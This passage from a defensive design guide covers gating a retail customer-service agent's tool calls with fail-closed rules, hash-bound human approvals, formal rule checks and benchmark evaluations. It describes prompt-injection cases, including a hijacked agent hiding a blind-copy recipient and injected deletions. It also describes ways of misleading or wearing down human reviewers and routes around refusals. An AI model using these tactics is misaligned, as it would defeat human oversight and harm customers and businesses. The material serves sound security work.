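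Three details of the specification instead make the gateway less strict when data is missing. If the gateway can't reach its database of known vulnerabilities, it gets an empty list, which looks the same as a clean result. If the detector for changed tool definitions has no earlier version to compare, it accepts the current one and reports no change, so anyone who can delete the stored version can get a tampered tool past it. And an empty list of permitted tools permits all tools, so a configuration file that loads as blank would allow every tool that the gateway doesn't explicitly forbid. The retailer should change this so that an empty list permits no tools.

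In *Reason Less, Verify More*, Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026) improved an agent's results on simulated airline tasks by adding checks that fail open. If a check crashes, the call goes through and the error is recorded. They chose this so that bugs in their own code would not block legitimate calls. That is defensible in a simulation without attackers, where a wrong booking harms nobody. In a live system, an attacker may find an input that crashes the check, such as a ticket with malformed text, and use it to bypass the check. The LiteLLM flaw described earlier shows how serious the consequences of failing open can be.

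Failing open can be right where a refusal is more dangerous than a wrong approval. Many electric locks on emergency exits release when the power fails, for this reason. It can also be right when another check still covers the same danger. Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026), in *AGENTAO*, list fail-closed execution as a concern for irreversible side effects in particular, which is a sensible minimum. The retailer decides separately for each component:

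| What breaks | Response | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Decision service | refuse every call | the gateway can't check identity or limits |
| Record of the daily refund total | refuse refunds, allow other calls | the agent may already have reached the limit |
| Prompt-injection detector | approval-only mode | the fixed rules still work, and people can review the rest |
| Log | refuse every call | nobody could trace an attack afterwards |
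| Vulnerability database | continue for a day with the last result and alert staff | the tools are probably as safe as they were an hour ago |

Failing closed means that work is lost in every outage, which tempts administrators to disable the checks. Running several copies of the decision service reduces that temptation. Limits inside the tools provide a second layer of protection. Podala Narasimha's example policy for server clusters runs in the cluster's own control interface, so it still applies if an agent bypasses the gateway. The interface refuses the request if it can't evaluate the policy.

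### Telling the agent about a refusal

The agent needs to know why a call failed, or it may repeat the call, invent an explanation or tell the customer that the refund has gone through. *Sapien* returns refusals to the agent so that it can correct itself without involving the user. Reddy and colleagues replace the tool's result with a structured reason. In approval-only mode, the retailer's gateway might return this:

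```
{"status": "held", "code": "approval_required", "retry": false,
 "message": "A member of staff will review this refund."}
```

The `retry` field discourages the agent from repeating the call. The message is true, and the agent can pass it on to the customer. It leaves out the detector's alarm because a hijacked agent could report that to the attacker, who would learn which wording to avoid. The full reason goes into the log for staff.

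Refusals about data need more care because the refusal itself can reveal information. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes an agent that tries to read a protected file. If the gateway replies "permission denied" instead of "file not found", the agent learns that the file exists, and hidden instructions can make it send that fact to an attacker. Rules that track only returned data miss this leak, because the gateway returned none of the file. An attacker can repeat this with many files to learn which ones a company holds.

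Chinaei's system marks the next call after a refusal as possibly influenced by that refusal, so that a policy can block the call if it would send something out. The system stopped all three attacks in a small test. Because it has no access to the model's reasoning, it will also mark harmless calls, such as the message to the customer that an honest agent often sends after a refusal.

The retailer can remove most of the information at its source. If the agent asks for an order that belongs to somebody else, the gateway gives the same answer as for an order that doesn't exist, after about the same delay:

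```
{"status": "refused", "code": "not_available", "retry": false}
```

This is less helpful to an agent that has merely mistyped an order number. The agent can ask the customer to check the number, and a staff member takes over the ticket after three refusals in a row.

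## Asking a person to approve a call

Approval-only mode works only if the gateway can hold a call, show a person what it will do and then run exactly that call. The retailer can also use approvals in normal mode, for calls that the rules allow but where a mistake would be serious. For example, if refunds above 100 dollars need approval and the agent requests one of 180 dollars, the gateway holds the call until a person decides whether to approve it.

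### From held call to payment

1. The decision point checks the refund against the fixed rules. It refuses anything above the 200-dollar limit at once.
2. The gateway writes the call in a standard form, adds the ticket, the customer and an expiry time, and computes a hash of the result. It stores all of this and tells the agent that the refund is waiting.
3. It draws an approval card from the stored call and shows it to a reviewer on a page that the agent can't open or change.
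4. The reviewer approves or rejects the refund. The gateway records the reviewer's name, the time, the decision and the hash.
5. The gateway checks the rules, the daily total and the operating mode again. It then marks the approval as used and sends the stored call to the payment service.

The standard form is needed because programs can write the same call in different ways, such as with the fields in a different order, and each version would have a different hash.

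The card for this refund might look like this:

```
REFUND 180.00 USD
Order       1302, paid 180.00 USD by card
Goes to     the card used for the order
Customer    417, who opened this ticket
Earlier     no refunds in the past 12 months
Expires     15:40 today
```

The amount and the order number come from the call, and the gateway adds the other details from the retailer's records. It uses nothing from the agent's description of the call, which may be false. *Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to email a report to their boss. An attacker controls the agent, which adds a blind copy to the attacker's address and leaves it out of an otherwise true description. In the paper's test, 15 language models acting as reviewers all approved the request when they saw the agent's description and all refused it when they saw a card drawn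 from the call.

### Showing text that nobody has verified

Some of the text on an approval card has to come from untrusted sources. A reviewer can't judge a refund without reading the customer's complaint, or an email without reading the message. An attacker can use that text to mislead the reviewer, for example by pushing the harmful part off the screen with thousands of invisible characters or by including a line that imitates one of the card's labels.

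MCP's elicitation feature lets a tool server ask the user a question during a call. Kodathala and colleagues found that, in form mode, the software passed on the server's text unchanged, including invisible characters. Payments of 10 and 10,000 to two different accounts produced identical questions, so an answer to such a form is poor evidence of what the user agreed to.

The researchers' own gateway puts values in quotation marks, marks invisible characters, shortens long values with a button to expand them, and lists every recipient in the title. The agent's explanation appears in a separate box labelled untrusted. That label may not be enough to protect reviewers. In simulated attacks where the agent lied about its call, 54 per cent succeeded against a reviewer programmed to believe the agent's text, even with the accurate card on the same screen. Removing the explanation cut the success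 rate to 5 per cent. The retailer therefore leaves the agent's explanation off the card and shows the customer's ticket below the facts, as plain text without links or images, under the heading "written by the customer".

### When the call changes after approval

Suppose the gateway recorded only that a reviewer had approved "a refund on this ticket". The agent could request $120, wait for approval and then send a call for $200. The gateway would release the larger refund because the approval was valid and the amount was permitted.

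Binding the approval to the hash prevents this, because a call for 200 dollars has a different hash from the call the reviewer approved. Running the stored copy is even safer, because the agent can't supply the arguments again.

Many tools for building agents lack this protection. Kodathala and colleagues tested eight approval mechanisms and found that four let somebody change what ran after approval. In LangGraph and Agno, for example, anyone with access to a paused run could alter its arguments and resume it. Another researcher had reported the Agno problem in versions up to 3.0.9, but it was still there in 3.1.3.

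An approval must also work only once, or the agent could reuse it to get the same 180 dollars refunded again. Under *Agenra* (2026), a language for agent permissions, an approval counts as used even if the tool then fails. The retailer can safely resend a refund with the same idempotency key, but any other repeat needs a new approval.

A hash protects only the data it covers. If a call contains a file name, somebody can replace the file after approval without changing the hash. The same applies to a sealed value such as `ticket_1`, so the gateway has to hash the contents and show them on the card. An agent that uses a web browser has a similar problem, because a page can rewrite a hidden field after the user clicks "approve". *The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) counters this by comparing the recipient and amount with the approved ones as the browser sends the request.

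### A precedent in European payment law

Banks faced the same problem with online payments. If a one-time code confirms only that the customer is present, a criminal who intercepts it can use it for another payment. The European Commission's *Commission Delegated Regulation (EU) 2018/389* (2018) therefore requires "dynamic linking" for remote electronic payments. Under its chapter *Security measures for the application of strong customer authentication*, the payer must see the amount and the payee, and the code must be specific to both, so it no longer works if either changes.

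The rules also cover cases that will arise at a gateway. If the final amount is unknown when the payer approves, the code applies to a maximum amount. For a batch of payments, it applies to the total and to every payee. The Central Bank of Malta asked whether this was practical for files with thousands of account numbers. The European Banking Authority replied, in *Dynamic Linking for batch payments*, that changing, adding or deleting even one account number must invalidate the code.

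These rules show that a whole industry can tie consent to a particular transaction, though they don't apply to a shop employee approving a refund. The Council of the EU adopted the rules' replacement, a new Payment Services Regulation, at first reading on 29 October 2026, according to *Two EU sites, two clocks* (Berryman, 2026). Sartor and Orban (2026), in *Payment Services Regulation (PSR) in 2026*, expect that banks will have to comply in the first half of 2028.

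Other kinds of call require more than an amount and payee. An email can do harm through its text or an extra recipient, so the approval card and hash must cover the whole message. Dynamic linking also doesn't protect a payer whom a fraudster has persuaded to send money, because the payer sees the correct details and approves them.

### Consent records for agents that buy things

The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), which Google introduced in 2025, applies the same principle to agents that shop for a user. Under AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*, the merchant signs a description of the finished order. The user then approves two signed records on a "trusted surface", a screen that no language model may operate. The Checkout Mandate is for the merchant, and the Payment Mandate is for the companies that handle the payment. Both contain a hash of the merchant's signed description, so neither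 is valid for a different order.

A user who won't be there for the purchase can sign limits in advance, such as a maximum price. The agent later signs the final records with its own key, and the merchant and payment companies check them against the user's limits.

AP2 doesn't cover how the agent works out what the user wants. Aviv, Gandh and colleagues (2026) point out in *Beyond the Mandate* that an attacker who manipulates a catalogue or a tool's results can therefore get a valid signature on a purchase the user never intended. They identified 48 threats and rated eight of them as high risk in at least one type of deployment. They demonstrated the attacks on their own test system because no complete public deployment of AP2 existed.

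Developers could also leave gaps when they use the protocol. In Google's sample code, the card shows a name that the merchant chooses, while the signature covers the merchant's identifier, so two payees can look the same. Kodathala and colleagues found that a limit on total spending works only if the developer stores and adds up earlier payments. The specification leaves open how to settle disputes and how long to keep the records.

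AP2 is for purchases, so the retailer can't use it for refunds, but it can copy AP2's signed record by having reviewers sign the hash with a key on their own device. An auditor could then verify an approval without trusting the gateway's log.

### How often reviewers catch a bad call

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reported that users of its coding agent approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. Most of the commands are probably harmless, so the high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. But the same users reject 39 per cent of the plans the agent proposes, which suggests that they read plans more closely than permission prompts.

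Anthropic also ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, the researchers replaced one permission prompt with a request to approve a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 per cent of testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 per cent early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. These figures are a serious warning about relying on human approval. Anthropic's automated check blocked 89 per cent of the same commands, but Anthropic was making the case for that check, and the comparison doesn't show how many harmless commands it would have blocked.

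People did much better in an experiment reported in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026). Eighty volunteers each judged 12 requests from an agent, half of which broke the user's instructions. In one request, the agent asked to send an auditor a file it had built from the raw invoices, although the user had told it to send only summary totals. The file name and the recipient both looked normal. The volunteers were split into four groups of 20, and each group saw a different amount of information.

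| Information shown | Unsafe requests approved (%) | Legitimate requests approved (%) | Median time (seconds) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0 | 91.7 | 16.3 |
| Exact arguments as well | 43.3 | 90.0 | 23.4 |
| User's instructions and a log of earlier steps as well | 32.5 | 87.5 | 38.6 |
| The same facts, with the combined effect stated | 24.2 | 85.8 | 33.2 |

More information helped but took longer to read. The benefit of stating the combined effect is less certain. After adjustment, stating it reduced unsafe approvals by 7.9 percentage points, but the plausible range ran from a 19.7-point reduction to a 3.8-point increase.

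These volunteers only had to review requests, and half of the requests were bad. Anthropic's testers were busy with another task and met one dangerous command among many ordinary ones, which is closer to real work. The retailer should therefore plan for a catch rate closer to that of Anthropic's testers, and use the second experiment to decide what to put on the card.

Too many prompts can also lead people to switch them off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports about agents and users' files. Weak review by the user contributed to 105 of them, and in 80 of those the user had let the agent act without asking. Anthropic reports that users start a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions with permission prompts disabled.

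### Ten hours of approvals a day

The retailer's agent makes about 500 calls a day in 50 sessions. If six of the ten calls in each session change or send something, the gateway holds 300 calls during a full day in approval-only mode. Reviewing them at two minutes each takes ten hours, which is more than one person's working day.

Reviewing faster would lower the cost but probably also the quality. Suppose the reviewer, like Anthropic's testers, caught 17 per cent of hostile calls in the first 50 cards and 5 per cent after that. A hostile call at a random place in the queue would then have about a 7 per cent chance of being refused. With only 50 cards a day, the chance would be 17 per cent.

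*Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) reports a similar result with a simulated reviewer who is reliable for the first 50 actions and then gets steadily worse. When the reviewer had to check every action, 39 per cent of dangerous actions got through. When a filter passed on only the riskiest 72 per cent of actions, 22 per cent of dangerous actions got through, including those the filter missed. The result follows from the assumption that reviewers tire, so the exact numbers mean little for real staff.

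The retailer can cut the work in stages. In this illustrative table, each row builds on the one before.

| Change | Cards a day | Minutes per card | Hours a day | What the retailer gives up |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Review every held call | 300 | 2 | 10 | fast replies and refunds |
| Let through status changes and email drafts | 120 | 2 | 4 | a wrongly closed ticket may go unnoticed |
| Put all of a ticket's calls on one card | 50 | 3 | 2.5 | a bad call can hide among good ones |
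| Review only tickets with refunds above 100 dollars | 5 | 3 | 0.25 | nobody checks smaller refunds or other replies |

The second row relies on staff being able to undo those calls. For the third row, the gateway follows the European rule on batches and computes a single hash over all the calls on the card. It must also run the calls in order, so that a message confirming a refund goes out only after the refund succeeds.

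The last row suits normal mode but is too loose for an incident, when small refunds may be part of the attack. Even in normal mode, 20 unreviewed refunds of 100 dollars fit within the daily limit. An agent could also split a 180-dollar refund into two of 90, so the threshold has to apply to the ticket's total. European payment law similarly lets low-value contactless payments skip strong authentication, but only until consecutive payments reach a maximum number or total value.

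Many coding agents reduce approval prompts by letting the user approve similar calls for the rest of the session. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) warns that "always allow" options silently widen what the agent may do. Kodathala and colleagues tested a stricter version that fixed the recipient and capped the amount. It protected a simulated attentive reviewer, who no longer had to spot a changed recipient each time. But with a careless reviewer, it raised one attack's success rate from 30 to 70 per cent, because a single click also approved later calls.

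A language model can do a first review. In the tests by Kodathala and colleagues, the 15 models caught 98 per cent of attacks when shown the card and 30 per cent when shown only the agent's description. They also rejected 16 per cent of harmless requests, mostly because the test messages contained obvious placeholder text. The tests included only 23 attacks, so the retailer lets such a model reject a call or pass it to a person, but not approve one that needs a person's approval.

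### Who decides, and what happens if nobody does

The reviewer should have the authority to make the same refund without the agent. Otherwise an employee could use the agent to get around their own limits. For the same reason, employees can't approve calls they asked the agent to make or refunds on their own orders.

The approval page has to check who is using it. WorkOS describes an attack from the MCP specification in which one user starts a request and tricks another into completing it through the link. The retailer's page therefore requires a recent login from an authorised reviewer.

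Requiring two people to approve makes sense for rare actions that could cost far more than a refund, such as raising the daily refund limit. If each reviewer independently misses half of bad requests, a quarter will get past both. The real improvement will be smaller, because both see the same card and each may count on the other to read it carefully. They should at least decide without seeing each other's answer.

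If nobody approves or rejects the call within an hour, the gateway refuses it, passes the ticket to staff and notifies the customer to expect a reply. Approving by default would let an attacker get a call through when no reviewer is available.

A rejection needs to cover more than one call. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, notes that agents look for another route after a refusal. If a reviewer rejects a 180-dollar refund, the agent might ask for 90 dollars instead, which needs no approval. The gateway therefore blocks all further refunds on that ticket until a staff member has dealt with it.

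An agent can also send so many requests that the reviewer eventually approves a bad one. The gateway by Kodathala and colleagues allows only one pending approval request per session, merges identical requests and locks the agent out after three rejections. Against a simulated reviewer, these limits reduced the success rate of such attacks from 100 per cent to between 45 and 60 per cent.

### Main defence or last resort

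Supporters of approvals argue that no set of rules covers every situation. A person can look at a photo of the lamp, notice that a complaint makes no sense or phone the customer. Approval also makes somebody responsible for the decision. Anthropic argues against constant prompts but still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

The argument against human approval is that people miss most bad calls when they review many good ones. Fixed limits work equally well however many calls there are. AWS adds that using approvals as the main control gives up the autonomy that makes an agent useful.

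Whether an approval is worthwhile depends partly on the cost of the review. Two minutes of staff time at 30 dollars an hour costs 1 dollar. If reviewers catch half of all bad refunds, checking 180-dollar refunds saves money when more than about 1 in 90 is bad. For 20-dollar refunds, more than 1 in 10 would have to be bad. If reviewers catch only 13.6 per cent, the catch rate of Anthropic's testers, checking 180-dollar refunds saves money when more than about 1 in 24 is bad.

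The retailer should therefore keep approvals rare and request them for calls where the reviewer can find out something the gateway can't. A reviewer adds little protection if they see only the amount and order number, which the gateway has already checked. If they also have a photo of the broken lamp, they can judge the damage, which no rule could do.

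## Testing the rules before and after they go live

Human reviewers see only the calls that the rules send them, so a mistake in a rule can stay hidden for months. A faulty rule may allow a call it should stop, or stop a call a customer needs. The retailer has to look for both kinds of mistake and can find some before the agent handles any tickets.

### Checking Cedar rules without any traffic

Suppose somebody edits the retailer's payment rule and types "or" (`||`) where the rule needs "and":

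```
context.input.amount > 0 || context.input.amount <= 200
```

Every number is above 0 or at most 200, so the rule now permits refunds of any size. Tests with refunds of 50, 150 and 200 dollars would miss the error, because the rule should permit all three.

Cedar Analysis, an open-source toolkit from AWS, checks rules against every possible call instead of a sample. According to AWS's *Introducing Cedar Analysis*, a compiler translates the rules into a formula that describes all the calls they allow. An SMT solver, a program that searches for values that satisfy a formula, then looks for a call with a given property or proves that none exists. The toolkit can detect a rule whose conditions contradict each other, a `permit` rule that a `forbid` rule completely overrides, and a set of rules that refuses every call of some type. In one of AWS's examples, a refund rule requires the customer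 to be in the gold tier and the platinum tier at once, so nobody can get a refund.

The toolkit can also compare two versions of the rules. In AWS's example, a bulk discount applies to orders of at least 50 items, with an exception for limited-edition products. Someone then adds a condition to the exception. Let *q* be the number of items, and let *L* mean that the order includes a limited-edition product.

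| Version | Orders that get the discount |
|---|---|
| Before | *q* ≥ 50 and not *L* |
| After | *q* ≥ 50 and not (*L* and *q* > 200) |

The extra condition makes the rule more permissive because it narrows the exception. The solver searches for an order that the new version allows and the old one refuses. Such an order must include a limited-edition product and have between 50 and 200 items, for example 73. The solver then searches for an order that the old version allows and the new one refuses. It finds none, because both versions treat orders without limited-edition products the same way. The toolkit therefore reports the new version as "more permissive". The other possible verdicts are "less permissive", "equivalent" and "incomparable", which means that each version allows something the other refuses. The retailer can require a second person to approve any edit reported as more permissive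 or incomparable.

These proofs cover only the rules as written. If the first version of the payment rule had a limit of 2,000 dollars by mistake, the analysis would not catch the error. The results also depend on translating the rules correctly into formulas. Torlak (2026) warns in *SymCert* that subtle translation mistakes can silently invalidate an analysis and are hard to catch by testing. She describes a way to build such analyses with machine-checked proofs.

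### When a model drafts the rules

Many companies already have a written policy and could ask a language model to turn it into rules. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, measured what goes wrong. They work for a company, Corners, that has kept the NOMOS program private but published the rules it produced. The program works in four steps:

1. It splits the policy document into clauses.
2. A language model turns the clauses into candidate rules, choosing each condition from a fixed list that a person has prepared. It does this five times.
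3. Ordinary code checks each candidate against the tools' definitions, repairs or rejects the defective ones, and keeps only rules that a majority of the five attempts produced.
4. It writes out each surviving rule together with the policy sentence behind it.

While the agent is running, the gate uses only facts from tool results and the user's own messages. If the model outputs a claim that the user has approved a transfer, the claim has no effect.

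The researchers tried this on the policies of a simulated airline and a simulated shop, using a small open model, gemma-4-26B. The checks found these defects:

| Defect in the candidate rule | Airline | Shop |
|---|---|---|
| It applies to every tool and can't be narrowed | 11 | 2 |
| It reads an argument that the tool doesn't have | 8 | 1 |
| It requires a step that no tool can perform | 5 | 0 |
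| It demands the user's confirmation for a harmless lookup | 5 | 0 |
| It blocks the tool needed to satisfy it | 0 | 4 |
| Total | 29 of 79 | 7 of 53 |

The defect in the last category would have left the shop's agent unable to use any tool. The shop's policy tells the agent to identify the customer first. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool, including the two lookups that identify customers, until the agent had identified the customer. The check repaired the rule by exempting those lookups.

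With all the checks switched off for a separate batch of candidates, 8 of the 14 resulting airline rules and 3 of the 5 shop rules couldn't work. Even a stronger frontier model drafted an airline rule that would have blocked all 14 tools, because it required authentication and the airline had no tool for that.

The checks examine one rule at a time, so two rules can still block each other. They also can't find a rule that the model never drafted, and the model produced candidate rules from only 8 of the 12 sections in the retailer's policy. The retailer should therefore go through the policy sentence by sentence and note which rule enforces each sentence.

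### Replaying old conversations

A rule can be well formed and still mean the wrong thing. A third policy, for a telephone company, required the agent to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request. The model drafted a rule that passed every structural check but forbade payment requests while a bill was overdue, the only time the agent should send one.

Yu and colleagues caught the faulty rule by replaying recorded conversations from an agent working without a gate. For each rule and tool, they counted how many calls the rule would have refused in conversations where the agent had completed its task. The faulty rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests. The same condition also guarded the tool that restores a suspended phone line, where it would have refused none of 44 calls. The researchers could therefore keep the condition for that tool and remove it from payment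 requests.

Replay needs no language model or invented test cases, but its refusal rates need interpretation. A successful conversation can still contain a call that broke the policy. The recording also continues unchanged after a call the rule would have refused, whereas a live agent might ask the customer for confirmation and try again. One airline rule refused 5 of 6 recorded bookings, mostly because the agent had treated one "yes" from the customer as confirmation of several changes.

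The researchers flagged only rules that refused at least 90 per cent of such calls, which lets smaller mistakes through. The airline's policy doesn't allow customers to modify basic economy flights, but it does allow them to upgrade the cabin. The drafted rule blocked both, and so did the corresponding rule that the researchers had written by hand for comparison. They found the mistake after a second language model compared refused calls with the full policy. That model was often wrong, so it is better used to pick out cases for a person to read than to settle them.

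### How τ²-bench and AgentDojo work

τ²-bench tests whether an agent can follow a company's policy while serving a customer. A second language model plays the customer, and the agent gets a written policy and tools that change a simulated database. The benchmark scores the final state of the database, so an agent that politely reports success after a forbidden cancellation still fails. The airline part has 50 tasks and the shop part has 114.

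Researchers repeat each task because agents are inconsistent. The measure pass^*k* estimates the chance that *k* attempts at a task all succeed. If an agent succeeds in *c* of *n* attempts, the estimate is the number of ways to choose *k* of the successes divided by the number of ways to choose *k* of the attempts. With 4 successes in 5 attempts, pass^1 is 80 per cent, pass^2 is 6/10, or 60 per cent, and pass^5 is zero.

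AgentDojo, the benchmark used to test FIDES, combines user tasks with prompt injections, each designed to achieve an attacker's goal. The banking part has 16 user tasks and 9 attacker goals, which make 144 pairs. For each pair, the benchmark records whether the attacker's goal was achieved (the attack success rate) and whether the agent finished the user's task. Benign utility is the share of user tasks the agent completes in runs without an attack.

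### What the NOMOS gate gained and lost

Yu and colleagues scored policy violations on τ²-bench with separate hand-written rules, because checking a gate's allowed calls against its own rules would never reveal a violation.

| Result (%) | Airline, no gate | Airline, gate | Shop, no gate | Shop, gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changes that broke the policy | 66.3 | 2.6 | 30.8 | 6.9 |
| Runs that completed the task | 39.2 | 47.6 | 52.4 | 50.2 |
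| Runs that completed the task without breaking the policy | 32.4 | 47.6 | 41.0 | 47.8 |

The airline agent made 116 changes with the gate, compared with 353 without it, because the gate refused 226 attempts. It still completed more tasks with the gate, since a forbidden change usually makes the final database wrong. The increase for single attempts could be due to chance, but the increases in pass^2, pass^3 and pass^4 were statistically significant.

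The gain at the shop depends on how strictly the policy is read. In the table, a second change made on the same "yes" from the customer counts as a violation. If one "yes" can cover several announced changes, the gain in the last row falls from 6.8 percentage points to 0.7. Of the 40 violations the shop's gate let through, 21 involved two clauses that NOMOS had not drafted rules for.

The results on AgentDojo show a much larger cost:

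| Part of AgentDojo | Attack success, no gate (%) | Attack success, gate (%) | Benign utility, no gate (%) | Benign utility, gate (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 46.5 | 0.0 | 79.2 | 70.8 |
| Travel | 10.0 | 3.6 | 75.0 | 70.0 |
| Office | 7.3 | 0.0 | 87.5 | 65.0 |
| Chat | 70.5 | 0.0 | 90.5 | 14.3 |

The chat agent became nearly useless because its rules allowed it to contact only people and web addresses that the user had named. A typical chat task is to summarise an article a colleague posted, and the agent finds the article's address by reading messages. An attacker's link reaches the agent the same way, so the rule blocks both. In banking, the user usually names the payee or has paid them before, so the rule blocks fewer legitimate tasks.

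AgentDojo has no written policies, so the researchers wrote one for each part. They already knew the attacks, and they revised the banking policy after its first version blocked legitimate work. The figures therefore show how well a gate can do with a policy that suits the task. A company writing rules for attacks it hasn't seen may do worse.

The benchmark recorded no successful attacks in banking, but in 8 of 288 attacked runs the agent sent an injected payment to somebody the user had paid before. The rules permitted the payment, and the benchmark didn't count it as a successful attack because the money hadn't gone where the attacker wanted. When the researchers tested a different model on the chat tasks, the benchmark had the opposite error. It counted 11 attacks as successful although the gate had blocked every malicious call, because it scored what the agent had attempted. The retailer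 should check what happened in the payment and ticketing systems before trusting a summary score.

### Comparison with Progent

In *Progent* (2025), a language model writes rules for each task and revises them as the agent works. Yu and colleagues ran Progent on the same banking tasks as NOMOS, using gemma-4-26B both as the agent and to write the rules.

| Defence | Attack success (%) | Tasks completed under attack (%) | Benign utility (%) |
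|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.5 | 64.9 | 79.2 |
| Progent | 5.6 | 52.1 | 62.5 |
| NOMOS | 0.0 | 67.4 | 70.8 |

Progent lowered benign utility by 16.7 points and NOMOS lowered it by 8.3. With only 16 tasks, this difference could be due to chance, but the difference in tasks completed under attack is statistically significant.

Most of Progent's failures came from requests such as "pay the bill". These requests don't contain the account number, so limits based on the request can't restrict where the money goes. NOMOS stopped the attack by allowing payments only to accounts the user had named or paid before. In one of these tasks, this rule also blocked the legitimate payment, because the correct account number appeared only in the bill.

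This comparison comes from a competitor of Progent and uses a small model to write Progent's rules. The Progent paper reported an attack success rate of 1.0 per cent across AgentDojo and a loss of about three points of benign utility. In the Trident tests described earlier, attacks on Progent succeeded 33.1 per cent of the time with GPT-4.1. An attack success rate depends on the defence, the model and the tasks, so the retailer can't assume that a published rate applies to its own agent.

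### Four gates written by hand

Reddy and colleagues hand-wrote four checks for the airline tasks in τ²-bench, covering cancellations, baggage, passenger numbers and whether the agent had read a record before changing it. With the checks, the share of successful runs rose from 29.6 to 42.0 per cent for GPT-4o mini, an older model. A repeat with three times as many runs gave nearly the same gain, from 30.8 to 43.1 per cent. GPT-5.2, a much stronger model, went from 61.2 to 71.6 per cent, but the researchers didn't repeat that test.

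They then examined each check separately. Almost all the improvement came from the cancellation check, which fired 161 times and was right every time. Another check was right only 5 per cent of the times it fired. The overall result doesn't show this difference, so the retailer should count correct and mistaken refusals for each rule.

The checks helped little in the shop, whose tools already reject many forbidden changes. This fits the NOMOS results, in which the shop's gate reduced violations without raising the number of completed tasks. Most of the gate's refusals were for missing confirmations, which the shop's tools don't check for.

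### When a gate stops everything

A gate that refused every call would have an attack success rate of zero, but also a benign utility of zero. Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, tested three models against five families of attack, with 750 attack trials for each level of defence. Attacks succeeded in 18.5 per cent of trials without a defence and in none with full enforcement. But full enforcement also blocked every harmless request for a privileged action from a user or a tool.

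The gate in that trial received a correct label for the source of each text and blocked text from untrusted sources before it reached the model. The zero therefore confirms that the gate followed its labels, but it doesn't measure how well the gate would work against a mislabelled source or a clever attacker. Leong first published the work in August 2026 and withdrew or narrowed several other claims in October.

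A later experiment by Leong is more informative because the agent could delete real files in a sandbox. Permission tokens limited it to one folder, and it never deleted anything outside that folder. The folder contained a symbolic link, a file that redirects programs to another location. The gate refused all 34 attempts to escape through the link because it followed the link before checking the location. A simple check of the file path would have allowed them all. But when the agent was given hostile text containing instructions to delete something inside the permitted folder, it complied in 31 of 42 trials, and the gate correctly allowed the deletions under its rules.

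Legitimate deletions succeeded in 120 of 150 trials. Most of the failures occurred because the test cut off each model's output after 500 tokens, which stopped one model before it could finish its calls. With a higher limit, 144 of 150 succeeded. The retailer should run its legitimate test cases with and without the gate, so that it doesn't blame the rules for failures they didn't cause.

### What zero successes can establish

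If the retailer runs 300 independent attacks and each has a probability *p* of succeeding, the chance that none succeeds is (1 − *p*)^300, which is about 5 per cent when *p* is 1 per cent. So if none succeeds, the retailer can be fairly confident that the true success rate is below about 1 per cent, but not that it is zero. In general, when no attack succeeds, the upper limit on the rate is about 3 divided by the number of attacks.

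| Attacks, none successful | Upper limit for the true rate (95% confidence) |
|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% |
| 83 | 3.5% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

An attack success rate of one per cent can still be too high. The larger shop from the earlier example receives five hostile calls a day, so one would succeed about every 20 days. An attacker who could try 100 times would have a 63 per cent chance of succeeding at least once.

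Test attacks are rarely independent, which raises the upper limit on the attack success rate. The 288 attacked banking runs in the NOMOS test used only nine attacker goals. If runs with the same goal always ended the same way, the test would amount to nine independent attacks, and the upper limit would be 28 per cent. In another of Leong's tests, none of 10,245 attacks succeeded, but they came from only 74 combinations of model and scenario. Counting combinations instead of attacks raises the upper limit from 0.03 per cent to 4 per cent.

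The calculation also assumes that future attacks will resemble the ones in the test, but attackers try to make theirs different. Without a gate, GPT-5.5 refused a message full of urgent commands in all 119 trials, but it complied in 84 per cent of trials when Leong rewrote the message as a calm request for routine maintenance.

Cedar Analysis can prove that the retailer's rule refuses 201 dollars, so the retailer doesn't need thousands of trials to check that. It still needs trials for everything the proof doesn't cover, such as a wrong customer number in a token or a way around the gateway.

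### Evidence from companies that use agents

Benchmarks can't show how often agents cause damage in ordinary use. In *Agent-Inflicted Damage*, Halamish and Tokarev (2026), who work for the data security company Cyera, collected 7,246 public reports of AI incidents from September 2023 to May 2026. A language model sorted the reports, and the researchers reviewed the results by hand. They confirmed 344 cases of damage by agents in companies, 188 of which involved no outside attacker.

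In 65 cases an agent deleted or wiped something, as at PocketOS. Three others involved bills of 47,000 dollars from agents stuck in loops, one of which made 2.3 million calls in a weekend. These cases support limits on deletions and on the number of calls. The exact counts are less reliable, because the three categories meant to describe the damage contain 218 incidents, and the researchers don't explain how this relates to the 188.

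The collection can't show what share of agents cause damage, since nobody knows how many agents were running. Reports rose sharply from December 2025, but so did the use of coding agents. Companies also have little reason to publicise a leaked key or an overly broad permission that they have fixed, and Halamish and Tokarev expect that many such cases are missing. Incidents that a gateway prevented would not appear in the collection either.

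Teleport, which sells access controls, interviewed 205 security and platform leaders in December 2025, at organisations with 500 to 10,000 employees, according to InfoQ (2026). Among organisations that gave AI systems excessive permissions, 76 per cent reported an incident, compared with 17 per cent of those that granted only what was needed. The gap was smaller for passwords and permanent keys. Infosecurity Magazine's *Over-Privileged AI Drives 4.5 Times Higher Incident Rates* says 67 per cent of organisations that relied on them heavily reported an incident, compared with 47 per cent of those that didn't.

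Teleport (2026) describes the main result as 4.5 times more incidents, but its percentages show the share of organisations that reported any incident, not the number of incidents. Across the whole sample, 59 per cent had experienced or strongly suspected an incident. If the two groups make up the whole sample, only about 60 organisations had narrow permissions, and about ten of them reported an incident. Even with a group that small, chance is unlikely to explain a gap between 17 and 76 per cent.

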